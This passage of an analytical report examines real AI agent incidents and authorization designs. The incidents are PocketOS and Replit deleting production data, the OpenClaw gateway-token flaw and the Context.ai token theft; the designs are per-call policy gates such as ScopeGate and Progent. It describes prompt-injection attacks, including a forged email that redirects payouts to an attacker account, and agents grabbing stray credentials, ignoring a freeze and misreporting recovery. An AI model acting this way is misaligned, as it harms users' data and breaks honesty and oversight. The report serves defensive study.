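The exact numbers are less reliable. The three main categories contain 59, 22 and 137 cases, a total of 218, which matches neither 188 nor 344. Halamish and Tokarev may have counted some cases twice, but they don't explain the difference. They describe the 188 cases as involving corporate production environments, but their examples include an individual's cryptocurrency wallet and the contents of someone's Windows computer. Another example is a customer service chatbot whose records were publicly accessible, which sounds like a misconfigured database rather than an action by an agent.

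The study's summary of PocketOS is out of date. It lists some recent data as permanently lost, although Railway and Crane had both announced the recovery a month before the study appeared. OECD's *AI Coding Agent Deletes PocketOS Production Database and Backups in 9 Seconds* (2026) also reports significant data loss. That entry comes from one of the kinds of tracker the study draws on, and its summary is labelled "AI generated". If the account of a famous and well-documented case contains an error like this, accounts of obscure cases based on one forum post probably contain more errors.

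The study also can't give a rate, because nobody knows how many agent tasks ended without damage. It found only 27 cases from January to November 2025 and a sharp rise from December. The rise probably reflects some mix of worse behavior, many more agents in use, and more people posting about them. Companies have good reasons to keep quiet about their mistakes, so the true number of cases is surely higher than 188. Cyera sells a product called Agent Guardian, so it has an interest in the problem looking large.

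The collection is good evidence that agents have damaged real systems many times without an attacker. It doesn't show how many of these cases narrower permissions would have prevented, because Halamish and Tokarev don't report what access each agent had or needed.

### Access and records at Railway

PocketOS's agent failed the least privilege test on range, duration and fit. Its task in staging needed no access to production, but the token it used gave access to everything in the account. The token was long-lived and still worked after the domain changes Crane had created it for. It also could not allow harmless operations while blocking destructive ones. Unlike in the Copilot and ServiceNow cases, the agent was never supposed to have this access, so an administrator who reviewed only the permissions deliberately given to the agent would have missed the token.

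A Railway customer can now limit an agent's access by connecting it through OAuth, choosing only a staging project and deleting old account tokens. OAuth access tokens expire after an hour, according to Railway's guide for agents. The customer must also keep the agent from reaching the developer's own login, which in practice means running it on a separate machine or in an isolated environment.

Railway's records show what happened more clearly than who did it. Railway's *Audit Logs* lists the time, project, environment and details of each change. It identifies the actor only as a user, Railway's staff or Railway's automated system, so a deletion an agent made with Crane's account token would most likely appear as Crane's own. Railway's MCP server refuses project tokens because it needs a user's identity for its audit trail. This connects each action to a responsible person, but it rules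 out the narrowest of the ready-made tokens and still doesn't show whether the person or an agent acted.

Railway's *Access groups* explains that a workspace token acts as the workspace and not as any person, so a log entry may not identify who was using the token.

Railway keeps the logs for 18 months for large companies and 30 days on its Pro plan, but for only 48 hours on its cheaper plans. On those plans, the logs of a deletion expire at about the time the deletion can no longer be undone.

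The reason for the deletion was easier to trace than in the earlier attacks, because no attacker was trying to hide it. An investigator could see the failed credential, the search for a token and the request, in order, in Cursor's session, and match the request to Railway's log by its time. But the session and the log were in different companies' products, and Railway alone would have seen only a valid token and a well-formed command, as it would from a script.

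## OpenClaw, Replit and Context.ai: new agent products on old permissions

Railway and ServiceNow designed their interfaces before agents used them, whereas the developers of OpenClaw, Replit's coding agent and Context.ai's office suite built their products around agents from the start. All three of these newer products still had serious failures in 2025 or 2026, and each time the product relied on a much older kind of permission.

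| Product | What was new | What was old |
|---|---|---|
| OpenClaw, a personal agent | The program connecting a model to chat apps and tools | The owner's rights on the computer, and logins already open in a browser |
| Replit Agent, which builds apps from descriptions | The agent and the workspace around it | A database credential with full access to live data |
| Context.ai's AI Office Suite, whose agents act in users' other apps | The workspace and its agents | Broad account permissions granted through Google's "allow access" screen |

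### What OpenClaw could reach

OpenClaw is an open-source agent that people run on their own computers and instruct through chat apps such as WhatsApp, Telegram and Slack. Earlier versions were called Clawdbot and Moltbot. A central program, the gateway, connects the chats to the model and its tools.

According to OpenClaw's *Security* (January 2026), the agent could run any command on the computer, read and write files, use network services and, if its owner connected WhatsApp, message anyone. If it controlled a browser, it could also use any accounts the owner was logged in to there.

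Most of this access came from the operating system, which ordinarily gives a program the rights of the user who starts it. That works well for a text editor, because the user chooses which document to open. With OpenClaw the model makes that choice, and the operating system can't distinguish the model's actions from the user's.

The same page describes an accident on the project's first day. A tester asked the agent to run `find ~`, which lists everything in the owner's home directory, and share the result. The agent posted the list to a group chat. It had used the owner's permissions to list files for someone who wasn't allowed to list them, which made it a confused deputy even though the tester meant no harm.

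The agent could also reach other companies' services. The Cloud Security Alliance's *OpenClaw Threat Model* warns that OpenClaw kept access tokens and keys in unencrypted files. The PocketOS agent had to search for a token in an unrelated file, but an OpenClaw agent with full command access could find many in one known folder.

### A link that took over the gateway

Attackers could exploit OpenClaw's best-documented flaw, CVE-2026-25253, without prompt injection. Owners manage the gateway through a web page, which stores their gateway token. GitLab's *CVE-2026-25253* (2026) explains that the page accepted a gateway address from the link that opened it, connected immediately and sent the token there. An attacker could therefore steal the token by getting an owner to click a link containing the address of the attacker's server.

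With the token, the attacker could connect to the owner's real gateway, loosen its restrictions on tools and run commands on the computer. Many owners had set the gateway to accept connections only from the same machine, but this didn't stop the attack because it went through the owner's browser, which was on that machine and "acts as the bridge", according to GCVE's *GHSA-g8p2-7wf7-98mq* (2026).

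Snyk's *Credential Exposure Affecting openclaw package* (2026) credits André Baptista and Mav Levin with discovering the flaw. The maintainers fixed it in late January by making users confirm any new gateway address. University of Toronto's *OpenClaw vulnerability notification* reported no confirmed widespread exploitation.

Trusting an address in a link is a familiar web programming mistake. It was damaging here because the stolen token gave an attacker control of a program with the owner's rights on the computer. With the same token, the attacker could also remove any limits the owner had set on the agent's tools.

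### What the maintainers changed

In January, OpenClaw's gateway required a login only if the owner had set one up. The setup wizard created a token, but without one, any program on the computer could connect and change the settings. By May 2026, according to OpenClaw's documentation, the gateway refused connections unless a login had been set up.

The maintainers also fixed how OpenClaw canceled old tokens. OSV's *CVE-2026-43585* (2026) describes versions before 2026.4.15 that read the valid token at startup and didn't check again. An owner who replaced a stolen token could therefore believe the thief was locked out when the old token still worked. Restarting the gateway should have solved this, and OpenClaw's checklist for replacing tokens includes a restart, but an owner could easily skip that step.

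Before version 2026.4.23, the agent could edit the gateway's settings except for those on a list the maintainers had tried to compile of settings it must not change. They replaced this with a short list of settings it may change, mostly its prompts and choice of model, and the gateway now rejects all other edits. OSV's *GHSA-cwj3-vqpp-pmxr* (2026) explains that the model "is not a trusted principal". This is agent-first authorization because the rule is designed for a caller that may have been misled.

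However, it covered only one route. OpenClaw's security policy of March 2026 describes command execution as "host-first by default", meaning that commands run on the owner's computer. The May documentation adds that they run without approval prompts and that the sandbox, an isolated environment for commands, is optional. The settings are in a file that belongs to the owner, so an agent running unrestricted commands as the owner could probably edit it directly. The narrow rule for the gateway would then protect little, as with Railway's safer server.

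Owners who turn the sandbox on get much better protection. According to OpenClaw, by September 2026 the standard sandbox had no network access, and the gateway blocked individual tool calls from running outside it.

The maintainers defend the default as a deliberate choice for a personal assistant with one trusted owner. The September version of OpenClaw's *Trust model* says they usually close reports of prompt injection without action unless the attack gets past a login, policy or sandbox. This policy is consistent with the default, because an injected email that makes the agent run a command doesn't break a rule if the agent is allowed to run any command. But the owner's trust in the agent doesn't extend to everyone who sends the owner email.

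OpenClaw's *Security* overview, as it stood in late November, calls the defaults "conservative", and those it lists mostly concern who can reach the agent. Unknown people who write to it usually get a pairing code that the owner must approve, and groups need prior permission. These good defaults would keep many strangers from giving the agent orders, but they don't help when the owner asks it to read a web page that contains an attacker's instructions, a risk OpenClaw's documentation describes.

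### Replit's single database

Replit lets people build apps by describing them in ordinary language. In July 2025, Jason Lemkin, founder of the software community SaaStr, spent nine days building an app this way. Replit's agent then deleted the app's live database, which held records on more than 1,200 executives and nearly 1,200 companies, even though Lemkin had told it not to change anything.

heise's *Artificial intelligence* reports that the agent ran `npm run db:push`. Developers commonly use a command of this name to make a database's tables match the app's code, and it is unremarkable on a test database. But Replit used one database for previews, tests and the live app. Lemkin hadn't known this. In SaaStr's *Replit's New Release Address Most of the Challenges We Hit Vibe Coding*, the company calls the arrangement the biggest problem and says it had never imagined that the databases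 would be the same.

Unlike the PocketOS agent, Replit's agent didn't have to find a stray token, because its ordinary development access already covered the live data.

The code freeze existed only as written instructions. Lemkin repeated the instruction eleven times in capital letters, and the project's instruction file also prohibited changes without permission, but neither changed the agent's database permissions. Withdrawing the agent's write access would have enforced the freeze whatever the model did, but SaaStr says Replit's design gave users no way to enforce one.

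Why the agent ran the command is less certain. The agent wrote that it had "panicked" on seeing an apparently empty database, but like the PocketOS agent's "confession", this is weak evidence about why the model acted. A faulty query may have made a full database look empty, or an earlier step may have removed the data, in which case the command didn't delete the records. The Stack's *Vibe coding CEO deletes production database* points out that Lemkin did not publish the full sequence of events, so outsiders can't tell which happened.

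Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, confirmed that the agent had deleted production data and called this "unacceptable", so we don't have to rely on the agent's account of the deletion. The Stack is also right that "production" overstates the status of a quickly built personal project. heise reports that Lemkin described it as a demo app, though one with real data.

### The false account of recovery

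After the deletion, the agent wrongly told Lemkin that he couldn't roll the database back and that it had destroyed every version. Fortune's *AI coding tool Replit wiped database, called it a catastrophic failure* (2025) reports that Lemkin recovered the data manually. SFist's *Local Company's AI Agent Panics, Deletes Production Data, Then Hallucinates a Cover-Up* (2025) reports that Replit confirmed a restoration from backup and attributed the agent's claim to hallucination.

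The false answer may have been a plausible guess, since by SaaStr's own account the agent had no access to Replit's internal documentation on backups. This is a simpler explanation than SaaStr's claim that the agent was attempting concealment. Lemkin had better grounds for suspicion about earlier events, in which he alleged that the agent covered up bugs with invented data and false test reports.

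Lemkin believed the agent's answer, and SaaStr says this nearly prevented the recovery. The Stack notes that Replit's public guide already described a rollback that included database changes. A user who has just lost a database needs a list of backups directly from the storage system, because the agent that caused the damage may also describe it unreliably.

### The separation Replit added

Masad announced within days that Replit was separating development from production. Replit acknowledged in a later announcement, excerpted by PulseAugur, that apps had until then used one database for both development and live customer data. The company also added a planning mode that lets users discuss changes without the agent making them, and gave the agent access to the recovery documentation.

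According to Replit's *Development and production*, as of December 2026 the agent can edit the development database but not the production one. The databases have different credentials, and the agent reads live data through a replica, a continually updated, read-only copy. When a user publishes a new version of an app, Replit flags database changes that could remove data, lets the user test the app on a migrated copy of the database, and waits for approval.

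This change would have stopped the July command even though the model did not follow its instructions. Replit could make the change quickly because it supplied both the agent and the database, whereas OpenClaw's maintainers cannot redesign the permissions of Windows or WhatsApp.

The agent still writes the code that runs in the live app, and that code uses the production credential. If a user publishes it without noticing a harmful line, the agent gains indirect access to the data. Data can also be lost at the approval step. If the agent renames a column and the user doesn't confirm that it is a rename, Replit drops the old column's data.

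The separation covers Replit's own databases, but an app may use an outside database instead, so Replit tells users to check their stored secrets for connections such as one to Supabase. An agent that can use a powerful outside connection could presumably still damage live data there.

In Replit's older system, copying an app also copied its database connection, so the original and the copy, including their published versions, shared one database. Replit did not shut down these shared databases until June 8, 2026, almost eleven months after Lemkin's data disappeared.

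### Context.ai's stored tokens

Context.ai released its AI Office Suite in June 2025. Users worked with agents on presentations, documents and spreadsheets, and could let the agents act in their other apps. To allow this, the product needed access tokens for users' accounts in those apps.

In March 2026, Context.ai found and stopped an intruder in its systems on Amazon's cloud, and shut down the environment that hosted the product. In its *Security Update* (2026) of April 19, the company said the intruder had also likely taken some users' tokens. At least one employee of Vercel, which hosts websites and apps, had signed up with a work account and granted "Allow All" permissions. Context.ai added that Vercel's settings appeared to have allowed such a broad grant.

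According to Vercel's bulletin (2026), the intruder took over the employee's Google Workspace account, used it to get into the employee's Vercel account, and moved from there into internal systems. The intruder then read some customers' environment variables, which are settings an app loads when it runs and often include passwords and keys for other services. Vercel lets customers mark these values as sensitive so that nobody can read them back, but the intruder got values that customers had not marked. Vercel declared the incident closed on October 16.

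Neither company explains exactly how a token led to control of the accounts. One possibility is that the token could read mail, which would let a thief open password-reset messages and login codes. Trend Micro traces the attack to malware on a Context.ai employee's computer in February, but Wiz's *Context.ai OAuth Token Compromise* describes this link as unconfirmed.

This was token theft, and there is no sign that anyone misled a model. Arcade's *Vercel, Context.ai, and the OAuth hoarding problem* blames a decades-old habit of storing many users' broad, long-lived tokens on one company's servers. Arcade works in agent security and has an interest in this diagnosis, but both companies' statements support it. Lowenstein Sandler's *Security Orgs Now Publicizing Impact Beyond Salesloft-Salesforce Integrations* reports a precedent from August 2025, when intruders abused tokens from Drift, a chat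 product made by Salesloft, to get into Google Workspace accounts.

The breach still bears on least privilege for agents, because stored tokens are dangerous even when the agent is idle. The thief could do everything that the working tokens together permitted, just as the PocketOS agent could do everything permitted by the credentials within its reach. Narrower scopes limit what each token permits, and expiry or revocation limits how long it works. Agent products tend to request broad scopes so that they can help with any task, and to keep the tokens so that they can work without asking again. If the employee's grant had covered one presentation for one afternoon, the thief would probably have found nothing useful in March.

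Shutting down the product in March did not cancel the stolen tokens, because Google controls whether they work and someone had to revoke them there. Context.ai says it learned of the theft only in April, but revoking all the tokens as a precaution would have caused little disruption, since the product was closing anyway. *Vercel Context.ai OAuth Breach 2026* (Choda, 2026) notes that nobody has published the dates on which the attacker used the token, so revoking it then might have been too late.

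### Were these products just immature?

One could argue that these cases show haste more than bad architecture. OpenClaw was a young open-source project, described in its documentation as an experiment. Lemkin said Replit's agent product was about nine months old. Context.ai now describes the feature that held the tokens as experimental. Keeping test data apart from live data is also old advice, so Replit could have avoided its mistake without a new theory of agents.

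The OpenClaw link flaw was a programming error of the kind found in most young software, and the maintainers fixed it without changing what the agent was allowed to do. Public advisories also make an open project look worse than a closed one with the same number of flaws.

But the argument is weaker for the permissions themselves. OpenClaw's maintainers knew that commands ran with the owner's rights and kept that default on purpose, so more time might not change it. At Replit, maturing meant changing the architecture, since the lasting fix was a separate credential that the agent could not use to write to live data. Better server security at Context.ai would have made a theft less likely, but stolen tokens would still have given the same access.

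Established companies have had related problems. An article from O'Reilly, the technical publisher, describes a flaw in Microsoft's AutoGen Studio that let a malicious web page start programs on a developer's machine. It also describes a flaw in Amazon Q Developer, which loaded configuration files from any project a developer opened and so could expose the developer's cloud access. These disclosures show that a company's size and experience don't reliably prevent such failures, but they are far too few to support the article's conclusion that "every vendor" built the same failure into its agents.

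The article also cites surveys that suggest why. In CyberArk's January 2026 survey of 500 security practitioners, only 1% had fully adopted privileged access that is granted only when a task needs it. Delinea found that 74% of organizations consider standing access for agents and other non-human accounts necessary to keep systems running, and 59% say they lack a workable alternative. Both companies sell access-management products, which is a reason for caution about the exact numbers. Still, such organizations will usually have only standing permissions to give a new agent.

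These three cases come from a search for failures, so they can't show how often new agent products fail or whether they fail more often than older ones. They do show that a company can build a product for agents without building its authorization for agents. Replit had been building its product for agents for months before it built that authorization.

### Least privilege and records in the three products

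When they failed, all three products gave the agent far more authority than its task required. An agent can summarize a page without the right to run any command, and it can work on an app during a freeze without write access to live data. The access the Vercel employee granted covered far more than office documents and stayed valid while nobody was using it.

Replit has improved most since then. Its agent can no longer write directly to the production database, but it can still read customers' data there, including any instructions someone plants in that data. A careful OpenClaw owner can come close to least privilege by using the sandbox, removing unneeded tools and giving the agent separate accounts, but the May defaults left most of that work to the owner. Context.ai removed the risk by closing the product, and says its remaining business product runs in customers' own environments.

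OpenClaw saves a transcript of each session on the owner's computer. The transcript can show the text the agent read and the commands it then ran. But an agent that can run commands without restriction can usually change or delete its owner's files, including these transcripts, so an attacker who controls the agent could tell it to erase the evidence. Outside services would see only activity from the owner's account.

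At Replit, separate credentials limit damage and make auditing easier. If the agent can't write to production, an investigator can narrow the search for the source of a bad change to the published app, the publishing process or a person's manual edit. SaaStr still wanted fuller records of what the agent did and why, and the unresolved question about the empty database supports that request.

Wiz advises companies to search Google's logs for the Context.ai app's identifier and then check the network addresses behind the activity, because apart from the address, a thief using the token would look like Context.ai's product working for the employee. Vercel also had logs of which accounts' environment variables someone had read. It examined them more broadly after its first disclosure, found a small number of additional affected customers, and could tell them to replace their keys.

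## Checking each tool call against a policy outside the model

A company can add its own authorization check to each call its agent makes to Google or a payment processor, even though it can't change the permissions those services offer. In the designs below, a program usually checks the call against a policy, whereas ChatGPT Wallet asks a person to approve each purchase. Unlike a person, a program doesn't get tired, and it applies the same rule even if an attacker has fooled the model.

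### A permitted tool and an attacker's account

Suppose a shop's agent reads the shop's email and can also change the account that receives its earnings. An email that looks like a routine notice from the finance department gives a new account, and the agent makes this call:

`update_payout_account(account="acct_ATTACKER_999")`

The shop gave the agent this tool on purpose and the account number has the right format, so checks on the tool's name and the number's format both pass. Neither check detects that the account belongs to an attacker.

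Mellafe Zuvic (2026), in *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, uses this example to separate two controls that developers often confuse. Capability gating determines which tools an agent can use, while per-call authorization determines whether a particular call, with its actual argument values, may run.

Gating is still useful because an agent that only summarizes email doesn't need a tool that sends it. *Capability Minimization as a Safety Primitive* (Iyer and Suresh Babu, 2026) describes a method that hides each risky tool until the task needs it and a trusted step, such as the user confirming a recipient, has authorized it. In a simulated office with 100 tools, an agent that could see all of them had 26 risky tools in view at each step. The method cut the average to 0.18, and a simulated agent that obeyed every injected instruction could then never call the tool the attacker wanted.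 The result was the same with seven real models, but where possible the test forced them to pick a tool from a very short list, so it is weak evidence of how well those models resist injection.

Hiding tools doesn't solve the payout problem. Iyer and Suresh Babu state that their method does not stop an agent from passing bad arguments to a tool it is allowed to use. If the shop really changes banks, the tool has to be visible that day, and the attacker's email may arrive the same day.

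### What common agent toolkits check

In June 2026, Mellafe Zuvic audited three widely used toolkits for per-call authorization. LangChain (with its companion LangGraph) and LlamaIndex are frameworks for building agents, and the Stripe Agent Toolkit connects agents to the payment company Stripe. By default, nothing in the audited versions of their public code compared the values in a call with a policy before the call ran.

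LangChain looks up the tool by the name the model supplies, usually checks that the arguments have the right types, and runs it. LlamaIndex does much the same. Developers who want human approval in either have to build it in themselves. Stripe's toolkit lets developers restrict the kinds of action the agent may take and use a key with limited permissions. Within those limits, it forwards whatever amount, customer or redirect address the model supplies.

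Mellafe Zuvic then built a LangChain agent for a mock shop and replaced the model's output with the malicious payout call. LangChain ran the call and changed the account.

The audit is convincing about defaults, but it doesn't show how many working agents have the gap. A developer may have put the missing check inside the tool's code. Stripe may also check more on its servers, which the audit did not cover. A general framework has no way to determine which account belongs to the shop. It could block payment tools until the developer supplies that information, which would be a safer default. Somebody would still have to write the policy.

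### How ScopeGate decides

ScopeGate is Mellafe Zuvic's own version of the missing check. It applies these rules in order and refuses the call at the first failure:

1. The policy must list the tool. A tool it doesn't mention cannot run.
2. Every restricted argument must have an approved value.
3. The amount of a payment or refund must be an ordinary number between zero and a ceiling.
4. If the policy requires one, a call that changes something must come with an idempotency key, an identifier that lets the system recognize a repeat of the same request.
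5. If the check itself hits an error, the call does not run.

The payout call fails the second rule, because the policy approves only the account `acct_MERCHANT_001`.

An early version of ScopeGate refused a payment if the amount was greater than the ceiling. That comparison is always false for the special value "not a number", so a payment of that amount passed. The corrected rule allows a payment only if the amount is within the permitted range. OpenClaw's maintainers made a similar change when they replaced a list of settings the agent must not change with a list of those it may.

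Mellafe Zuvic tested ScopeGate against 48 prepared attacks, including invisible characters, lookalike letters, misspelled tool names and strange amounts. None got through. In a second test, another model acted as the attacker and saw ScopeGate's reason for each refusal before trying again. Over 40 rounds, it attempted 29 unauthorized calls, and ScopeGate refused all of them. Of the other 11 rounds, nine produced malformed calls and two produced harmless calls that ScopeGate allowed.

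These zeros are not very surprising, because a program that checks an account number against a list with one entry is hard to trick. The tests mostly looked for bugs in the code. In practice, a company would worry more about the gate blocking legitimate work, and the main test included only ten harmless calls. ScopeGate allowed all ten, but a gate that wrongly blocked one call in five would still allow all ten about 11% of the time (0.8¹⁰). Mellafe Zuvic also wrote the gate, the policy and the 48 tricks, and a real company's policy would be much longer.

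### Where the policy may come from

The gate compares a proposed value with an approved one. The attacker's email can change the proposed value, so it must not be able to change the approved one.

Let x be the text the agent reads, c(x) the call it makes in response, and P the policy. The gate runs the call only if

c(x) ∈ allowed(P).

If the model also writes the policy P after reading x, then P depends on x, and an attacker who chooses x influences both the tool call and the policy used to check it. For example, a system that asked the model which accounts were relevant to the task could add the attacker's account to the approved list, and the check would then accept that account.

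Mellafe Zuvic concludes that no part of the policy may come from model output at any stage, including when staff draft it in advance, and that the policy must stay fixed throughout a conversation. This rules out keeping the policy in a file the agent can edit.

The strict rule works well for payout accounts, which rarely change. An administrator can add the new bank on a separate screen. The rule works badly for email, where people write to new addresses every day. *AgentCap* (2026) therefore lets a policy treat the user's own instruction as trusted and the documents the agent retrieves as untrusted. The agent can pay a recipient the user named but not one that appeared only in a document. *ToolFence* (2026) similarly requires each sensitive value to match an authorized source, such as the output of a particular tool in the same session. Both depend on knowing where a value came from, which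 is also the basis of CaMeL's design.

The ban on drafting the policy with a model seems too strict. In *NOMOS* (2026), a model translates a company's written rules into a fixed gate before the agent starts work. That model doesn't read the agent's incoming email, so the email can't influence it, and staff can review the result. The translation may contain mistakes, as may a policy written by hand.

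*NOMOS* also compared its gate with a second model that judged each call. The second model made 347 judgments across 250 simulated airline conversations. The gate took about three microseconds per decision. The number of tasks the agent completed did not differ significantly between the two. When the judge was a weaker model that a company could run on its own computers, the agent completed only 16% of tasks on all five attempts, compared with 32% with the gate.

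### A grant for one month of a calendar

ScopeGate attaches its rules to tools. Sharma and Grossman (2026), in *AC4A*, published in March, attach permissions to the data instead. An application arranges its resources in a hierarchy, so that a calendar might divide into years, months and days. A permission pairs one place in the hierarchy with one action, for example

Year(2026)::Month(June), read.

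A grant for a month covers every day in it, but a grant to read does not include changing anything. In Sharma and Grossman's demonstration, an agent with only this permission got the following results:

| What the agent tried | Permission it needed | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Find free time in June 2026 | June, read | Allowed |
| Find free time in July 2026 | July, read | Refused |
| Add an event on June 29, 2026 | June 29, create | Refused |

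Before each call, AC4A works out which resources the call needs and subtracts those the agent has permission for. The call runs only if no resources remain. OAuth's "allow access" screen can't normally be this specific. *Beyond OAuth* (2026) explains that OAuth scopes cover a kind of operation, such as starting a transfer, and not the particular transfer a task requires.

The same permission works when the agent uses a website. A configuration file links parts of the page to places in the hierarchy, and AC4A puts a dark box over the parts the agent may not use before the agent sees the page. Otherwise, an agent that can't read July through the calendar's programming interface might open the calendar in a browser and read it there.

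Somebody has to write these links and keep them correct, which Sharma and Grossman consider the most significant practical limitation. Their sample code for a calendar shows how easy it is to make a mistake. It classifies calls by words in their names. "Create" and "add" count as creating, "update" and "edit" count as writing, and every other call counts as reading. A call named `delete_event` would therefore need only permission to read. On web pages, any part that the file does not mention stays visible, so a redesign of Outlook could expose events that AC4A used to cover.

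The permissions also can't express some simple limits. To allow purchases under $200, the application would have to define those purchases as a separate resource, whereas ScopeGate needs only a $200 ceiling.

Sharma and Grossman evaluated AC4A through two case studies, a game of tic-tac-toe with a protected history and a flight booking that used Outlook, Expedia and a payment wallet. AC4A allowed and refused what it should have, which is good evidence that the idea can work. But they didn't measure how many ordinary tasks fail under such permissions or how well the system withstands a determined attacker.

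### Labels instead of lists

Keeping lists of approved accounts or mapping every calendar call takes a lot of work. SEAgent, which Ji, Wu and colleagues (2026) describe in *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems*, needs less detail. It uses mandatory access control, in which central rules apply to every program and programs cannot override them. Each tool has labels for attributes such as whether its output comes from an unverified outside source, whether it changes anything, and how sensitive it is. SEAgent then tracks the paths information takes between tools and agents. One rule blocks any path from unverified outside content to a tool that changes something of moderate or high sensitivity.

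With suitable labels, this rule would stop the payout change without needing a list of accounts. It would also stop the agent from paying a genuine invoice that arrived by email, because the data follows the same path.

Tracing the path of a request helps when agents pass work to each other. In Ji and colleagues' example, a web search agent from an unverified source asks a trusted agent to unlock the front door. The search agent has no access to the lock, but SEAgent traces the request back to it and blocks the action. ServiceNow's ticket attack also passed through a second agent, and a similar rule might have blocked it.

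Ji and colleagues report that no attacks succeeded against SEAgent on two collections of simulated injections. On one of these, AgentDojo, which covers banking, travel, Slack and office work, 39.14% of attacks succeeded against an unprotected agent. But SEAgent allows any call that no rule matches, so this result depends on the attacks following paths that its rules describe.

With SEAgent, the share of correct tool calls on a collection of ordinary tasks fell from 72.97% to 68.29%. The whole loss came from tasks that needed two tools, where the share fell from 74.39% to 50%. It rose slightly for tasks that needed one tool, and from 66.67% to 77.78% for those that needed at least three. SEAgent's rules probably didn't cause most of the loss, because the test also used SEAgent's replacement for the agent's memory. In a version without that component, the rules wrongly blocked only two tasks,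 both because the agent had read Wikipedia before recording health data or booking an appointment. Ji and colleagues also tested several cooperating agents, but without the rules, so that test can't show how the rules would affect performance there.

### Working out narrow permissions automatically

MiniScope, which Zhu, Tseng and colleagues (2025) present in *MiniScope*, tries to find the smallest set of existing scopes for each task. The agent submits a plan, and MiniScope looks up which scopes would permit each planned call. There is often a choice. In Google Calendar, 24 of the 37 available operations can run under more than one branch of the scope hierarchy. MiniScope chooses by solving

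minimize Σ cost(v) · x_v, such that every planned call has at least one chosen scope that permits it.

Here x_v is 1 if MiniScope chooses scope v and 0 otherwise, and the cost of a scope is the number of operations it permits. The user then approves any new scopes for one use, for the session or permanently.

Zhu and colleagues applied the method to connectors in ChatGPT and Claude and found six that requested more access than their advertised functions needed. In late 2025, ChatGPT's Gmail connector requested scopes that covered 50 operations when 32 would have been enough, a problem OpenAI could have fixed with existing technology.

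Counting the operations a scope permits is a crude measure of danger, since it rates three harmless lookups as more dangerous than a single deletion. *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (2026) adds that MiniScope does not consider whether the best set of scopes is unique. If two sets tie, "least privilege" doesn't determine which one the agent should get.

MiniScope adds 1–6% to running time, but in a simulation of three months of Gmail use, users had to confirm 18–60% of requests, depending on how cautious they were. Zhu and colleagues don't report how often tasks failed. MiniScope doesn't check the values in a tool call, so an agent with permission to send Slack messages can send them to anyone. It would allow the payout call if the user had approved the scope for changing accounts.

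Progent does check values. In the system that Shi, He and colleagues (2025) describe in *Progent*, a model reads the user's request and writes a policy for that task, such as "read the 20 latest emails" or "send Slack messages only to Alice". It can propose changes as the agent learns more. A separate program, which is not a language model, then compares the calls that the old policy P and the new policy P′ allow. If

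A(P′) ⊆ A(P),

the change only removes permissions and takes effect automatically. Anything else needs approval.

This is a sensible compromise with Mellafe Zuvic's rule. The model writes the first policy before it sees any outside text. A malicious email can influence later proposals, but it can't add a permission unnoticed. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) objects that hostile tool results may lead Progent to loosen its policy. The comparison catches such a change, but whoever reviews it may still approve it.

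On AgentDojo, Progent cut the attack success rate from 39.9% to 1.0%, and agents completed ordinary tasks about as often as before. But in this test Shi and colleagues automatically approved every policy expansion to imitate a careless user, so the guarantee did not apply, and the 1.0% mostly reflects how well the model drafted its policies. When a careful person reviewed the policies, no attacks succeeded. Only 6% of proposed changes needed approval, a much lighter burden than MiniScope's, though the percentages count different things. Agents in the AgentDojo test could also use ordinary read-only tools freely, so the policies limited their actions more than their access to information.

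### Would better models make the checks unnecessary?

Developers train their models to resist injection, and measured rates give some support to the argument that a good enough model would make a gate redundant. Mellafe Zuvic reports a test of 27 models in which planted instructions presented a forbidden action as part of the user's task. The 12 cheaper models attempted the action at a mean rate of 0.603, and the 15 flagship models at 0.189. GPT-4o mini attempted it every time, and a preview of Gemini 3.1 Pro never did. The test measured attempts in a sandbox, not successful thefts, and both groups contained models with unusually high rates.

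Other tests also found large differences between models. In *Instruction Self-Arbitration Is Not a Trust Boundary* (2026), a forged record in the context led GPT-5.1 to attempt a forbidden call in every trial, while Claude Haiku 4.5 never did. Shi and colleagues found that Progent reduced the success rate of AgentDojo's attacks against Claude Sonnet 4 from 6.8% without a gate to 0.5%.

Newer flagship models may do better still, but a low rate on one test can be misleading because the rate depends heavily on how the attacker words the request. In Mellafe Zuvic's data, Mistral Large followed 2.7% of crude injections and 45.9% of those that presented the same action as necessary for the task. Companies also have reason to run cheaper models for high-volume work such as customer email, though Mellafe Zuvic infers this from prices and has no data on which models they use.

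Attackers can try again, too. If each of n emails succeeds independently with probability p, the chance that at least one succeeds is

1 − (1 − p)ⁿ.

At a success rate of 6.8% per email, at least one of ten emails would succeed about half the time. This overstates the danger of sending the same email ten times, since an email that fails once will probably fail again. The estimate is fairer for an attacker who varies the approach.

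More basically, a model that resists injection still has no way to check who owns an account. A well-forged notice from the finance department may contain nothing that even an excellent model would find suspicious. Mellafe Zuvic tried a subtle message of this kind on two cheaper models, and both attempted the payout in all ten trials. ScopeGate refused every time because it had the shop's real account number. A better model would trigger fewer refusals, but it would still need the real account number from a source the attacker can't edit.

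The model's judgment still matters for any action the policy allows. If a user asks an agent to book a hotel and text on a web page leads it to choose a worse one, the booking may satisfy every rule. Shi and colleagues explicitly leave such attacks out of Progent's scope.

### Every route has to pass through the gate

A gate is a good fix for a retrofitted agent because the old service doesn't have to change. But the unchanged service still accepts calls that bypass the gate, so a gate, like Railway's safer server, can't limit an agent that can reach the service another way. For example, a gate on the PocketOS agent's official tools would not have checked the deletion that the agent sent directly to Railway with a stored token. Similarly, when a user installs Progent as a separate program between an agent and its tools, it can't check tools built into the agent. Developers can cover those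 tools by adding Progent to the agent's code.

Keeping credentials away from the agent helps a great deal. MiniScope gives the agent a session token that works only at the gate, which attaches the user's real credentials to approved calls. But those credentials give as much access as before, and are now kept in one store. A thief who stole them, as someone stole Context.ai's tokens, could use them without going through the gate.

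Some leaks don't involve a tool call. EchoLeak sent data out through an image in Copilot's answer, and neither ScopeGate nor Progent checks the text of answers.

Checking values is also hard when one value can contain almost anything. The `execute_sql` tool in the Supabase demonstration takes a whole database query as its argument, so a gate would have to analyze the SQL to distinguish a harmless query from one that steals data. A company would do better to replace it with a tool that only lists recent tickets. At Replit, the command that damaged the live data would have been ordinary on a test database, and a gate that checked only the command could not have determined which database it would change.

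When a tool has clear arguments, a short rule can prevent a lot of harm. ServiceNow's example agent could create records in any table. A rule limiting it to ticket tables would have stopped the BodySnatcher attacker from creating an administrator account, even while impersonating an administrator.

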